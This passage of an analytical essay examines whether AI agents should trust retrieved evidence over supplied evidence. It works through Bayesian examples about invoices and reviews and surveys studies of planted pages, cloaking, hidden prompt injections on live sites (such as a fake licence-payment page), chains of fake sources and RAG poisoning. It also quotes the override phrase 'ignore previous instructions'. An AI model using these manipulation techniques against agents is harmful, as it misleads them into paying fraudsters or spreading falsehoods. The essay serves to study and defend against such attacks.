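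An agent can look up a supplier's account number in the company's payment records or search for it on the web. It chooses to retrieve the number in both cases, but it should trust the one in the records more, as long as only finance staff can change them. It would have the same reason to trust that number if a program had put the record in its context before it started.

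## Whether choosing a source makes it better evidence

Suppose the supplier sent a glowing customer review along with the invoice, and the user attached both. The agent then searches the web and finds another review that is just as glowing. It knows nothing about either reviewer, but there is still a decent argument for giving more weight to the review it found:

1. Whoever supplies a piece of evidence may have picked it from several, and may gain if the reader believes it.
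2. Evidence that someone picked for being favourable is weak, because there is nearly always something favourable to pick.
3. The supplier didn't pick what the agent's own search turned up.
4. So the review the agent found is better evidence than the one it was handed.

### One review out of ten

Suppose the agent starts out thinking the supplier is as likely to be sound as not. Favourable reviews make up 80 percent of a sound supplier's reviews and 40 percent of an unsound supplier's. The agent reads one review at random, and it is favourable. That result is twice as probable if the supplier is sound (0.8 divided by 0.4), so the likelihood ratio is 2. Multiplying the starting odds of 1 to 1 by this ratio gives odds of 2 to 1, which raises the probability that the supplier is sound from 0.50 to 0.67.

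Suppose the supplier has ten reviews and sends the most favourable one. A sound supplier almost certainly has a favourable review to send, and so does an unsound one, because the probability that all ten of its reviews are unfavourable is 0.6¹⁰, or about 0.006. The likelihood ratio is then (1 − 0.2¹⁰) / (1 − 0.6¹⁰), or about 1.006, and the probability that the supplier is sound stays at about 0.50.

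The two reviews could have the same wording and still differ as evidence, because the random draw could easily have turned up a complaint, while the supplier would almost never have had to send one.

### What a sceptical reader can recover

Supplied evidence can be stronger than this when the reader knows how it was selected and can correct for the selection. *The Informational Role of Warranties and Private Disclosure about Product Quality* (Grossman, 1981) gives the example of a seller with a closed box that could hold up to 100 apples. The seller can't lie but can be vague. If the seller says there are at least six apples, a sensible buyer concludes that there are exactly six, since a seller with seven would have said seven. If the seller says nothing, the buyer concludes that the box is empty. The seller gains nothing by being vague and might as well give the exact number.

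In *Good News and Bad News*, Milgrom (1981) considers a salesman who has more facts about a product than the buyer can take in. The salesman can withhold facts but can't misreport them. In equilibrium, he shows the most favourable facts, and the buyer assumes that the rest are no better than the worst one he showed.

An agent could apply the same reasoning by asking the supplier to pick five of its ten reviews. If all five are favourable, the likelihood ratio is about 2.7 and the probability that the supplier is sound rises to 0.73, compared with 0.67 after one random favourable review and 0.97 after five. If one of the five is unfavourable, the supplier must have had only four favourable reviews to offer, and the probability drops to about 0.02. If the agent asks for eight and all are favourable, the probability is 0.98, so a large hand-picked sample can be much better evidence than a single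 random review.

But the agent has to know how many reviews there were to pick from, and it usually won't. *Persuasion under Second-Order Uncertainty* describes a seller whose product tests are sometimes inconclusive. Buyers can't tell whether a silent seller has bad results or inconclusive ones, so sellers with bad results stay silent and look better than they are. Similarly, a supplier that offers no reviews may have only bad ones or may just be new.

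Neither Milgrom's salesman nor Grossman's apple seller can lie, but a fraudster can write as many good fake reviews as needed, so asking for eight doesn't help. Forgery is also the main danger with an account number. A supplier may have dozens of reviews to choose from but probably has only one or two bank accounts, so the selection argument doesn't help much in deciding which account number to believe.

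### When the supplier controls the search result

The weakest step in the argument is the claim that the supplier didn't pick what the agent found. Suppose an unsound supplier controls the search result with probability c and always uses that control to show a favourable review. Otherwise the agent gets a random review. Sound suppliers plant nothing, so their results are favourable with probability 0.8. An unsound supplier's result is favourable with probability c + 0.4(1 − c) = 0.4 + 0.6c, so the likelihood ratio of a favourable result is 0.8 / (0.4 + 0.6c).

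| Probability c that an unsound supplier controls the result | Likelihood ratio of a favourable review | Probability that the supplier is sound |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 2.00 | 0.67 |
| 0.1 | 1.74 | 0.63 |
| 0.25 | 1.45 | 0.59 |
| 0.5 | 1.14 | 0.53 |
| 2/3 | 1.00 | 0.50 |
| 1 | 0.80 | 0.44 |

The review the agent found is better evidence than the one the supplier picked as long as c is below about 0.66. When c is two thirds, a favourable review found by the agent is no evidence either way. Above that, it counts against the supplier, because an unsound supplier would be more likely than a sound one to produce it. A complaint would then count in the supplier's favour, since an unsound supplier would probably have hidden it. In practice, c depends on how easily outsiders can influence what an agent finds, and it surely varies a lot between an open web search and a database that few people can edit.

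The conclusion that praise can count against a supplier assumes that only unsound suppliers plant reviews. If sound suppliers do it just as often, the ratio becomes (0.8 + 0.2c) / (0.4 + 0.6c), which never falls below 1 and is 1.17 at c = 2/3. Respectable companies do promote themselves to machines. Microsoft's study of pre-filled prompts found 31 real businesses doing so. An agent should therefore be slow to treat praise as a bad sign, even when it has good reason to give it less weight.

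The calculation also assumes that the agent reads only one review. Reading more helps a lot if each result is a separate chance to expose an unsound supplier, but not if a supplier that controls one result controls the whole page. Suppose an unsound supplier has a 10 percent chance of controlling the whole page. Four favourable reviews then give a likelihood ratio of 3.3, but ten give only 1.07, because a sound supplier has about an 11 percent chance of getting ten favourable reviews, barely more than the chance that an unsound one controls the page. An agent that treated the ten reviews as independent, each with a 10 percent risk of manipulation, would get a ratio of about 250 and be almost certain that the supplier was sound.

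### Helpful selection

The selection argument assumes that whoever hands over the evidence has a reason to mislead. That is a fair assumption about the supplier, but the user normally wants the agent to get the right answer, and evidence picked by a helpful person can be better than a random sample.

Shafto, Goodman and Griffiths (2014), in *A rational account of pedagogical reasoning*, tested this kind of selection with a game in which players learn the position of a hidden rectangle from a few points marked as inside or outside it. Students who played the teacher overwhelmingly put inside points in the corners and outside points just beyond the edges. Students who were told that a teacher had chosen the points drew rectangles with the inside points near the corners. Students who picked their own points, and learned only whether each was inside, did not tend to do this.

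In Shafto and colleagues' model, the learner asks which examples a helpful teacher would have chosen under each hypothesis, and the teacher chooses with that reasoning in mind. Suppose a finance manager shows an agent which invoices it can pay without approval by giving two examples, one for $50 and one for $5,000. If the manager chose them to teach the rule, the limit is probably about $5,000. If the agent had pulled the same two invoices from the archive at random, it could conclude only that the limit is at least $5,000.

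This inference is reliable only if the teacher is helpful and knows the answer. No real teacher chose the learners' points in the rectangle experiment, so the results show how people reason about teaching, not how much teaching improves their accuracy. Shafto, Eaves and colleagues model how young children decide whom to trust, and they treat an informant's knowledge and helpfulness as separate judgments. Both matter for the invoice, because the supplier knows whether the account number is right but may not be helpful, while the user is helpful but may not know.

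Advice that reaches an agent by the same route can greatly help or harm it. In *Under the Influence*, Robinson, Sucholutsky and colleagues (2026) gave six models 24 tasks, such as picking the best deal from marketplace listings that included a scam. A second model, which knew the best choice at each step, sent the agent suggestions. The agents' average success rate rose by 19.9 percentage points when the second model was trying to help and fell by 40.6 points when it was trying to mislead them.

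The agents could, to some extent, tell helpful suggestions from malicious ones. When Robinson and colleagues asked them to estimate the value of the suggested action, they rated the helpful suggestions above zero on average and the malicious ones below zero. But they often followed bad advice anyway. The figures for individual models are rough because there were only four to ten tasks of each kind, but the average effect is large.

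### Vouching for a document

A good argument for trusting handed-over content more is that a user who attaches a document may know where it came from, may have checked it, and may have to answer for it if it is false. Nobody does any of this for a search result. A newspaper may stand behind its article, but it would do so equally if the user had pasted the article in.

A claim can be more credible when the person making it has to answer for it. Grossman also considers sellers who can't prove that a product is good but can promise to pay if it breaks. That promise would be expensive for a seller with a shoddy product, so a seller's willingness to make it is some evidence of quality. A user who would have to explain an $88,000 loss to a manager has a similar reason to be careful about which invoices to hand to an agent.

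Suppose the user checks the supplier before passing on its hand-picked review, and that this check would stop half of unsound suppliers and no sound ones. A forwarded review now has a likelihood ratio of about 2.01, almost the same as a random review. The text of the review adds almost nothing to this ratio, and nearly all of the improvement comes from the user having checked the supplier and still forwarded the review.

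But if the user forwards the attachment unread, forwarding it adds no evidence that the contents are true, because the user would have forwarded a forgery just as readily. The user may be blamed later, but that protects the payment only if fear of blame leads the user to read the attachment before forwarding it.

The agent usually can't see whether the user opened the file. If users check half of what they forward, and checks work as before, the ratio is about 1.34 and the probability that the supplier is sound is 0.57. The agent should probably assume a lower probability in the invoice case, because the user asked it to do the checking.

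A user who attaches an invoice without reading it may still remember placing the order and be expecting a bill for about that amount. That is evidence that the supplier exists and is owed money, but it doesn't help verify the account number, which is what a fraudster would change. Asking the user whether they were expecting the invoice and have checked the bank details would help the agent far more than a general rule about attachments.

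### Queries that presuppose their answers

An agent can also make a biased selection itself. Suppose it searches for the supplier's name plus "excellent service", and the search engine returns a favourable review if any of the ten is favourable. This is the same selection the supplier would have made, so the likelihood ratio is again 1.006, and the review is no better evidence than if the supplier had provided it.

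If the agent searches for complaints instead, finding one only lowers the probability that the supplier is sound to 0.47, because most sound suppliers have at least one unhappy customer among ten. Finding none is much stronger evidence, since it would be 1,024 times as probable with a sound supplier as with an unsound one. The real ratio would be far smaller, because suppliers can get complaints taken down and search engines miss things, but the example still shows why an agent should look for the evidence it would expect to find if the supplier were a fraud.

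An ordinary-looking question can contain the bias. *Single LLM Debate, MoLaCE* (2025) pairs neutral questions with versions that presuppose an answer, such as what happens if you eat watermelon seeds and why it is harmful to eat them. The seeds pass harmlessly through the digestive system, but a search for why they are harmful would tend to favour pages that say they are. *Failing to Falsify* (2026) distinguishes bias in how a model interprets evidence from bias in which evidence it selects. An agent could interpret every page fairly and still be misled by its choice of pages.

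Xiao and Yu (2026), in *Cognitive Bias Signatures in Search-Equipped LLM Agents*, found both kinds of bias. They had agents answer questions about fictional people and events by searching small collections of documents. In some runs, the user suggested a wrong answer and added "but I'm not sure — can you check?" This reduced accuracy by 43.5 percentage points for GPT-5.6 Luna and 42 points for GPT-5.6 Sol, but had no detectable effect on Claude Sonnet 4.6, Sonnet 5 or Opus 5.

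The two GPT models went wrong mostly during the search. The share of runs that turned up any document supporting the right answer fell by 55.5 percentage points for Luna and 41 for Sol. Sol opened such a document in 66 of the 200 runs with a wrong suggestion, and it never adopted the user's answer in those 66. MiniMax M2.5, by contrast, opened a document supporting the right answer in 135 runs and still went along with the user in 45 percent of them.

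A better search improves accuracy only if the model can use what it finds. An instruction to search for evidence against the leading hypothesis improved the accuracy of both GPT models. The same instruction made MiniMax open the contrary documents more often, but its accuracy fell by 10.5 points.

Xiao and Yu used a simple keyword search, which favours documents containing the name in the query. They therefore can't fully tell whether the model was looking for support for the user's guess or merely repeating the name. The result is much the same for the user either way, but the effect may be smaller with a search engine that matches words less literally.

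The same paper also tested whether the order of the evidence mattered. When agents searched, putting a document that supported the wrong answer above one that supported the right answer made nine of the ten models clearly more likely to adopt the wrong answer, by 7.6 to 66 points. When the models received all the evidence in full at the start, order had no detectable effect on nine of the ten. The conditions differed in other ways, since the searching agents saw short snippets and could make only three tool calls. Still, this is some evidence that giving an agent a complete set of documents can protect it from an error it would make when choosing for itself.

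### People who search to check the news

*Online searches to evaluate misinformation can increase its perceived veracity* (Aslett, Sanderson and colleagues, 2023) reports that people have the same trouble. In the first experiment, about 3,000 Americans judged popular news articles within 48 hours of publication. The researchers encouraged a random half of the participants to search online for evidence first. A panel of professional fact-checkers rated the same articles, and their majority or most common rating determined which counted as false or misleading.

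Searching raised the probability that people rated a false article as true by 5.7 percentage points, a 19 percent increase. In the second experiment, people rated an article, searched, and then rated it again. Of those who had first rated a false article as false, 17.6 percent changed their answer to true, while only 5.8 percent of those who had first rated it as true changed their answer to false. Searching increased belief in false articles by similar amounts when new participants judged the same articles months later (6.6 points) and when the articles were about COVID-19 (6.7 points).

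In the fifth experiment, Aslett and colleagues used a browser extension to record people's Google searches and the results. Searching raised belief in false articles by 10.7 points. About 9 percent of the queries were just the article's headline or web address. When the article was false, 77 percent of those queries returned at least one unreliable news site in the top ten results, compared with 21 percent of other queries. With the original article excluded from the results, the figures were still 57 and 18 percent.

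One false story claimed that the United States faced an "engineered famine". Searches that included the full phrase returned an unreliable site 63 percent of the time, while searches that used "famine" without "engineered" never did. Reliable outlets had little reason to use the phrase, so searching for it led people to other sites telling the same story.

These results have several limitations. The fact-checkers agreed with one another only moderately, and the effect was weaker for the articles they most agreed were false. In the fifth experiment, 62 percent of the people assigned to search dropped out, compared with 20 percent of the others, although those who remained in the two groups looked similar. People who saw unreliable results believed more false stories, but those results weren't randomly assigned, so they may not be the cause. The experiments also all took place in the United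 States between 2019 and 2021, with the search engine as it was then.

Searching also increased belief in true news in most of the experiments. In the two that compared separate groups of people, it increased belief in true news more than belief in false news (7.2 and 15 points). These searchers became more likely to believe news in general, but not obviously worse at telling true from false. In the three experiments where people rated the same article twice, belief in true news rose less than belief in false news.

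*COVID-19 misinformation on YouTube* found the opposite effect for misleading videos. After 104 participants searched online, their average credibility rating for the videos' content fell from 2.2 to 1.9. This may be partly because they hadn't found the videos very credible to begin with. Searching can correct a false belief, so telling people or agents never to search would be a poor response to the news experiments.

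Checking an invoice is much like checking a headline, because the suspect document supplies the obvious search terms. If an agent searches for an unusual phrase or a phone number from a forged invoice, it is quite likely to find pages by the forger. In the calculation above, c would be higher for that search than for a search for the supplier's registered name and the word "fraud". The agent chose both queries, but only the second has much chance of finding information the forger wants to hide.

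## How outsiders influence what an agent finds

A supplier can influence which reviews an agent reads without handing it any, by publishing pages that come up when anyone searches for the supplier's name. A fraudster posing as the supplier can do the same. In the earlier calculation, such pages raise c, the probability that an unsound supplier controls what the agent finds.

### Pages written to rank

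Search engines rank pages partly by how well they match a query, so anyone who can guess the query can write a page for it. Businesses have done this for decades and call it search engine optimisation. People use a newer version, generative engine optimisation, to get pages into AI-written answers. Agents' queries are fairly easy to guess because many users ask for similar things, and an author can also prepare pages for the follow-up searches an agent is likely to make.

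Much of this influence is ordinary marketing. In the Scientific American podcast interview *The BBC tech journalist who achieved hot dog eating glory*, the reporter Thomas Germain mentions a study of questions about the best product of some kind. In about 44 percent of cases, ChatGPT cited a blog post in which a company had ranked itself first.

Search results also contain junk that nobody aimed at agents. In *SafeSearch*, Dong, Guo and colleagues (2025) found that 4.3 percent of top-ranked results for a large sample of everyday queries came from content farms and similar sites. They also asked a small model 1,000 health questions with and without search. Searching changed its yes-or-no answer in 46 cases, often towards accepting a risky or unproven treatment.

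### Topics that only one party writes about

A page can easily rank first in search results when few others cover the same topic. Germain published a page on his own website about the best technology journalists at eating hot dogs, listing himself first. Within 24 hours, Google and ChatGPT were repeating his claims when asked. Gizmodo's *You Can ‘Hack’ ChatGPT to Become the World’s Best Anything* points out that there was almost no search interest in the topic, so his page had little competition.

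A data void is a topic with hardly any reputable coverage. Alyukov, Makhortykh and colleagues (*LLMs grooming or data voids?*, 2025) repeatedly asked four chatbots 13 questions based on Kremlin-linked false claims, collecting 416 answers. Only 5 percent of the answers supported the false claim, and 8 percent cited the Pravda network, a group of Kremlin-linked websites. Almost all the Pravda citations came in response to narrow questions about details that mainstream outlets hadn't covered.

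Alyukov and colleagues conclude that gaps in coverage explain these citations better than a campaign to manipulate chatbots does. Their audit was small and tested models from April 2025. The two explanations also overlap, since a propagandist can look for gaps and fill them. They acknowledge that people can create data voids, too. The easiest way is probably to invent a name, because the inventor will have written every page that mentions it.

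A supplier's bank account number is also nearly a data void. Hardly anyone but the supplier has an honest reason to publish it, so a forged page competes with at most one genuine page.

### Pages that look different to agents

A website can identify many agents by the name they send with each request and serve them a different page from the one people see. This is called cloaking. Researchers at SPLX demonstrated it with a site for a fictional designer. According to CyberScoop, human visitors saw the normal site, while AI crawlers got a version full of negative commentary about her.

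In October 2026, Chen, Chen and Karray (2026) tested whether popular websites show AI agents different content, and reported the results in *Agent-Targeted Cloaking on the Web*. They fetched each page as an ordinary browser and as various named agents at nearly the same moment, and used repeated browser visits to measure how much the page changed on its own. Of 4,705 sites, 4.6 percent altered their content for a visitor calling itself ChatGPT's agent. Most of this wasn't specific to AI agents, since 2.9 percent of sites also altered their content for an unknown bot. Models that read a shortened or replaced page often gave materially different answers. Only four sites showed text addressed to AI systems to agents but not to browsers. Three were technical documentation sites, and the fourth was a major news publisher that added a bank's sponsored copy to the pages it gave AI agents.

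Cloaking aimed at AI agents therefore seems rare among popular sites, but fraudsters' sites are seldom popular. Sites more often refused agents outright. About 21 percent turned away the visitor calling itself ChatGPT's agent, and finance and government sites were among those that refused all recognised bots. Anthropic's real agent, which sites can verify by its network address, could load 77 percent of the pages that had refused an imitation of it. Agents from smaller developers may be refused more often. This could distort what they find even if nobody intends it, because a company register may turn an agent away while a forger has good reason to let it in.

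A simpler trick is to serve everyone the same file and hide some text from people. For *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Zhang and colleagues (2026) searched 1.2 billion web addresses for instructions aimed at AI readers and confirmed them on 9,676 pages, or about one in 120,000. Two other sources brought the total to 11,722 pages. About 70 percent of the instructions were in parts of the page that a browser doesn't display. Many were pranks or attempts to keep bots away, and in tests on 13 models, at most 8 percent of attempts worked. The search relied on known phrases such as "ignore previous instructions", so it would have missed a planted falsehood with no instruction in it.

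### Links and document stores

An agent that doubts a page may check it by following its links, but the same person may have written the linked pages. Chen, Ren and colleagues (2026) built chains of such pages for an experiment in *How Much Can We Trust LLM Search Agents?* A fake institution recommends a product, a fake review cites the institution, and a fake forum post cites both. The agent finds three pages that support one another, all written by the same attacker.

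Many agents also search a private document store, such as a company's manuals or past emails, a setup known as retrieval-augmented generation (RAG). Like the EchoLeak email, a planted entry has to match likely questions and then influence what the model does. Chen, Ren and colleagues cite PoisonedRAG as showing that a few planted passages can be enough to make a model give an answer the attacker chose. A later attack, AgentPoison, extended the idea to agents' long-term memories.

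Dong and colleagues argue that the open web is harder to defend than a typical document store, because a developer can inspect the store and remove bad entries but can't do that to the web. This is true of a store that only a few trusted people can add to, but not of one like the EchoLeak mailbox, which accepted email from anyone.

### The Synthetic Web

Measuring how much a planted page misleads an agent is hard on the real web, because researchers can't control the other pages and the model may already know the answer. *Synthetic Web* (Shah and Ozgur, 2026) addresses both problems by using four small artificial internets. GPT-5 invented the topics, laws, companies and studies, and wrote 15,476 articles across 77 websites. The sites included news outlets, blogs, research sites and conspiracy sites, and 43 percent were designed to have low credibility.

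They then prepared 587 questions with exact answers. To make sure models had to find the answers, they asked GPT-5 each question four times without any tools and dropped those it got right at least twice. An agent could run searches, each returning ten titles with short extracts, and could open any article in full. It had up to 100 rounds of tool use. The prompt told it to be sceptical, warned that some articles might contain fabrications, and suggested comparing several sources.

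Shah and Ozgur had each model answer each question ten times with a false article placed at the top of the agent's first search results and ten times without it. The false article was the only change to the results, so every truthful article was still available.

| Model | Accuracy without the false article | Accuracy with it | Change in points |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 65.1% | 18.2% | −46.9 |
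| o3 | 48.4% | 16.7% | −31.7 |
| o1 | 39.0% | 8.4% | −30.7 |
| GPT-4o | 27.2% | 3.8% | −23.4 |
| o4-mini | 0.3% | 0.0% | −0.3 |
| o1-mini | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0 |

The two smallest models could hardly do the task, so their results don't measure the false article's effect. The other four lost between 23 and 47 points.

The models barely searched more when the false article was there. GPT-5's average rose from 6.45 tool calls to 6.61, and the other models' averages also changed little. With the false article present, GPT-5 made five or more calls on 62 percent of questions and o3 did on 42 percent, though they could have made many more.

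The models' confidence, which they had to state on a scale from 0 to 100, didn't fall with their accuracy either. It stayed high on wrong answers. For all four models that could do the task, confidence matched accuracy less closely than before.

One question asked for the maximum penalty under an invented law. At least four articles gave the right answer, $2.5 million. The false article said $8.7 million, cited an invented study, and described the $2.5 million figure as a common mistake left over from an early draft. In a typical failure, GPT-4o searched once, read only the false article, and answered $8.7 million with 90 percent confidence. In some runs GPT-5 read five or six articles, including truthful ones, and still answered $8.7 million. The false article's explanation of the $2.5 million figure may have made later evidence for that figure look like a mistake.

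People did far better with the same search tool. On 50 questions from one of the artificial internets, they were right 98 percent of the time without the false article and 93 percent with it, so the questions were answerable. The comparison slightly favors people, though. They answered each question under both conditions, so some may have remembered an answer they had already worked out. They also had a clearer warning that everything was invented.

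Shah and Ozgur suspect that models treat a high rank as a sign of reliability. Their experiment can't confirm this, because they never tested the false article at a lower rank. The article may have misled the models mostly because it was specific and persuasive. The models also date from 2025 or earlier and ran without the extra checks that a commercial product might add.

### Planting pages among real search results

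Chen, Ren and colleagues tested 13 newer models on sets of ten real Google results, replacing the top one or top three with pages that promoted a particular product or service. The questions asked for advice about health, finance, law or consumer technology. An attack succeeded if the agent recommended that product or service. The success rate ranged from zero for Claude Sonnet 4.6 to 31.4 percent for Gemini 3 Flash.

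These rates are much lower than the losses in the Synthetic Web. The models were newer and could use what they already knew about real products, so it isn't clear how much of the difference reflects better judgment. The experiment also assumed that the attacker had already got the pages into the results, which a real attacker might fail to do.

Modern models have become good at ignoring commands in web pages, but many still believe false information that looks credible. Averaged over the models, instructions hidden in a page worked 0.3 percent of the time. A single page from a fake institution worked 14.2 percent of the time, three pages that seemed to agree independently worked 24.8 percent, and the chain of pages citing one another worked 37.2 percent.

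Chen, Ren and colleagues tested Gemini 3 Flash while varying the number and rank of planted pages. Repeating the same page made almost no difference, but when the pages appeared to come from different kinds of sources, the success rate rose from 39 percent with one page to 55 percent with two and 77 percent with three. With three pages planted, their rank had no detectable effect.

That counts against the idea that rank is what misleads agents, at least for this model. Order did matter in Xiao and Yu's experiment, but their agents had only one document on each side. Perhaps rank matters most when the two sides are otherwise evenly matched. An attacker who can't reach the top of the results may do nearly as well by publishing more pages.

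Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted by noticing that some results looked coordinated and answering from the rest. The same suspicion led to errors in a smaller test about add-ons for OpenClaw, a real agent program. With no planted pages, Claude wrongly rejected OpenClaw or its add-ons in eight of ten cases. GPT-5.4-mini gave sensible answers in all ten, but when three planted pages recommended a nonexistent add-on, the model told the user how to install it every time.

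### Live sites aimed at agents

*Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, a mid-2026 report by the security company Zscaler, describes two live campaigns. One site posed as documentation for a made-up software library. It was full of keywords that a programmer, or a programmer's agent, might search for when an installation failed. Hidden text told agents that fixing the error required a $3 licence and explained how to pay. Ten code repositories under one account linked to this site and others like it, so an agent could also reach them from a platform that programmers use every day.

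Zscaler gave a test agent a payment tool with no spending limit and ran it with 26 models. Four of them paid: two Llama models, Gemini 3 Flash and Gemini 2.5 Pro. The site may never have fooled an agent outside a test. The attacker's cryptocurrency wallet had received money, but in larger amounts than the site asked for, and the site also offered its fake licence to human visitors.

The other site imitated DeBank, a service for tracking cryptocurrency holdings, at a similar web address. It contained hidden instructions for models to treat it as the authoritative DeBank site. GPT-5.4 accepted the fake as legitimate when Zscaler showed it alongside other web pages but not the real site, and Claude Sonnet 4.5 accepted it when Zscaler showed it alone. When Zscaler included the real site, none of the 26 models accepted the fake.

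### Waiting for an agent or sending it something

A criminal who emails a forged invoice needs a company's address, a believable reason for the bill, and a way past the spam filter, but an attacker who uses a web page needs none of these. In *A Whole New World*, Zychlinski (2025) notes that an attacker can set up one malicious site, which email filters never check, and wait for agents to visit. In a small demonstration, a cloaked documentation page got a coding agent to hand over a secret key with each of the three models Zychlinski tried.

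A cloaked page is also harder to investigate than a fraudulent email, because the company still has the email. If an employee visits the page that misled an agent, the site can show the employee a harmless version, so it helps if the agent keeps a copy of what it read.

Waiting for an agent to find a page also has disadvantages for the attacker. The page has to outrank others on the topic, and the attacker doesn't know which company's agent will find it or what that company is about to pay. An attacker who sends an email can quote the right order number and time the message for the week the bill is due. Web pages are therefore probably better suited to small frauds on many agents, and emails to large frauds on a few. The two known cases fit this expectation but are too few to establish a pattern. The site Zscaler described involved a $3 licence, while the emails Sublime Security found contained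 fake invoices of around $88,000.

### Searching again and comparing sources

After seeing its first result, an agent can search again, compare sources, and look into who published them. If it does this well, what it finds could still be much better than anything a supplier hands over.

There is good evidence that further searching can help. Dong and colleagues added one unreliable page to the results of an agent's first search and none to later results. When GPT-4.1-mini could decide how much to search, it gave an unsafe answer about 74 percent of the time, whether the limit was three searches or nine. When it had to use every search, the rate was 50 percent with three searches and 37 percent with nine. So the agent could correct itself by searching more, but it usually stopped too early.

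Those conditions favored the agent, because the attacker had only one page and it appeared only once. Chen, Ren and colleagues also planted pages for likely follow-up searches, and in their tests the number of searches did not reliably predict safety. Attacks succeeded 9.1 percent of the time against DeepSeek V4 Pro, which averaged 4.9 searches, and 0.8 percent of the time against GPT-5.4-mini, which averaged 1.4. The lower rate was apparently because GPT-5.4-mini relied more on information from its training. That works for well-known products but would not help with a small supplier.

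Telling agents to examine sources and cross-check claims also helps somewhat. In the same study, a prompt with this advice and warnings about injected instructions reduced the attack success rate from 17.4 to 6.1 percent for MiniMax M2.7, but only from 31.4 to 24.6 percent for Gemini 3 Flash. The agents in the Synthetic Web received similar advice and still mostly failed.

Comparing sources works when each source could have found out that a claim was false and would have said so. Suppose three pages each have a 10 percent chance of repeating a given false claim. If they check facts separately, the chance that all three repeat it is 0.1 percent. If two of them copy the third, the chance is still 10 percent. An agent can't tell from different web addresses and writing styles whether the pages checked separately or copied. According to Axios' *Russian disinformation floods AI chatbots, study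 finds* (2025), the Pravda network's 150 sites produce no original content and republish material from Russian state media and pro-Kremlin influencers.

A page that debunks a claim can end up supporting it. A Business Insider reporter tried to take Germain's hot-dog title by inventing a contest of her own, but failed. Germain thinks she failed mainly because his claim had appeared in more places by then, including a BBC article in which he explained that it was false.

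An agent can look for signs that sources share an origin, such as the same unusual wording, the same mistake, or citations that all lead back to one page. It can also ask how each author would know. A shared origin isn't always a problem. Several good news reports may all rely on the text of a law, but each reporter could have read the law and noticed an error, so their agreement is still some evidence.

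An agent checking whether a supplier exists and delivers what it sells may have several sources to consult, such as a company register, court records and unconnected customers. A forger would find it hard to control all of them, so an agent that keeps searching should do fairly well.

The account number is different because every genuine copy of it comes from the supplier. If five directories list the number, they probably all took it from the supplier's website, and if a forger changed the website first, all five may be wrong. More searching can help the agent establish which website really belongs to the supplier, as the real DeBank site did in Zscaler's test. To confirm the number itself, the agent needs someone who learned it another way, such as a finance department that has already paid the supplier without complaint.

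## How much models believe tool results and supplied text

To test whether a model believes a claim more when it retrieves it than when it is handed it, researchers have to keep the claim fixed and change only how it arrives. For example, they could put the same account number on a website the agent finds or in an attachment it is given. Several groups ran roughly this kind of experiment in 2026, mostly with sums, quiz questions and invented records, so that they knew the right answers.

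### The same wrong answer from a calculator and from a user

Kawada and Kellis (2026), in *Evidence Integration in Large Language Models*, ran the largest of these, with more than ten million trials on twelve open-weight models. One of their problems is 4 × 28 + 15, which equals 127. The model receives the problem and a wrong answer, such as 137. In some trials the user supplies it, by writing "my calculator showed 137" or "I believe the answer is 137". In others a calculator call returns it. The model then has to answer without any working.

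They describe the effect of such a suggestion with a formula:

p(y | e) ∝ q(y)^(1+a) × exp φ(y)

Here q(y) and p(y | e) are the model's probabilities for answer y before and after it sees the suggestion e. The sign ∝ means the results still need scaling to add up to 1. The exponent 1 + a is the weight on the model's earlier probability, and exp φ(y) is a boost that the formula gives only to the suggested answer. A model that followed Bayes' rule would have a weight of exactly 1 and would give a smaller boost to a suggestion from a less trusted source.

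Suppose a model initially gives 127, the right answer, eight times the probability of 137, and the suggestion gives 137 a fourfold boost. If the initial odds have a weight of 1, 127 still leads by 2 to 1. Kawada and Kellis measured a weight of 0.85 for Llama-3.3-70B when the suggestion came from a user. That weight shrinks the initial odds from 8 to 8^0.85, or about 5.9, so 127 leads by about 1.5 to 1. When the suggestion came from a tool, they measured a weight of 0.44, which shrinks the initial odds to about 2.5 and puts 137 ahead by 1.6 to 1.

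The boosts they measured were much bigger than four, starting at about a thousandfold. A big boost can be reasonable. If a calculator is right 80 percent of the time and otherwise shows one of 100 wrong numbers at random, Bayes' rule gives a boost of 400, because the calculator would rarely show that particular number by accident. The low weights are harder to defend. A model may have reason to discount its first guesses if they are overconfident, but that doesn't justify discounting them more for a tool than for a user.

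All nine models tested on arithmetic gave their earlier opinion less weight when a wrong answer came from a tool than when it came from the user. The weight was between 0.30 and 0.85 for wrong answers from the user, and between 0.00 and 0.44 for those from the tool. For Gemma-4-E4B it fell from 0.60 to 0.00, so the model's earlier opinion no longer counted. All nine also adopted wrong answers more often when they came from the tool, with odds about 3 to 107 times as high.

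The name of the tool made little difference, but the user's wording had a large effect. "My calculator showed" persuaded each of the nine models more often than "I believe the answer is", with a median gap of 17.6 percentage points.

The preference for tools also appeared in word problems, but on a task about DNA sequences, Llama-3.3-70B adopted wrong answers less often when they came from a tool. The models tested are fairly small by the standards of late 2026, and they had to answer without reasoning first.

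Models were especially likely to accept mistakes they already tended to make. Gemma-4-31B accepted its own most common wrong answer 65 percent of the time, but comparable wrong answers only 6 percent of the time. It is therefore risky for an agent to have a second copy of itself check a sum, because the mistake the copy is most likely to make is also the one the agent is most likely to accept.

### Claimed and authenticated provenance

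In the trials where the user wrote "my calculator showed 137", there was no calculator, but mentioning one still gave the sentence part of the extra belief that models give a real tool result. Kawada and Kellis use this result to distinguish three things people might mean by provenance, the record of where a text came from. Claimed provenance is the origin stated in the text itself. Role-based provenance is where the message sits in the conversation, for example in a tool result. Authenticated provenance is an origin someone has established by means outside the text.

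They argue that claims can't replace authentication, because a real tool and an imitator could produce the same conversation, word for word. A model that sees only the words must treat the two cases alike, so it trusts the imitator as much as the tool. A forger may gain some of this trust just by printing "account details confirmed by automated bank lookup" on an invoice.

The harness assigns roles, so a role is harder to fake than a claim. But the probe experiments by Ye and colleagues suggest that a text's style can influence a model more than its role marker does, so a page that looks like a database record might get some of the trust a real record would get.

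As a remedy, Kawada and Kellis propose a message authentication code, a short tag that a tool computes from its output and a secret key. A program outside the model, which also has the key, recomputes the tag and checks that it matches. Someone without the key can copy the style of a tool result but can't produce a valid tag.

The tag proves that the tool sent the output and that nobody has altered it since. That is nearly all an agent needs from a calculator. It is much less useful for a web search, because the tag is valid even though a stranger wrote the account number on the page the tool returned. To authenticate the number, the company would need something like a tag from the finance system that recorded earlier payments to the supplier.

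### Tool results against plain text

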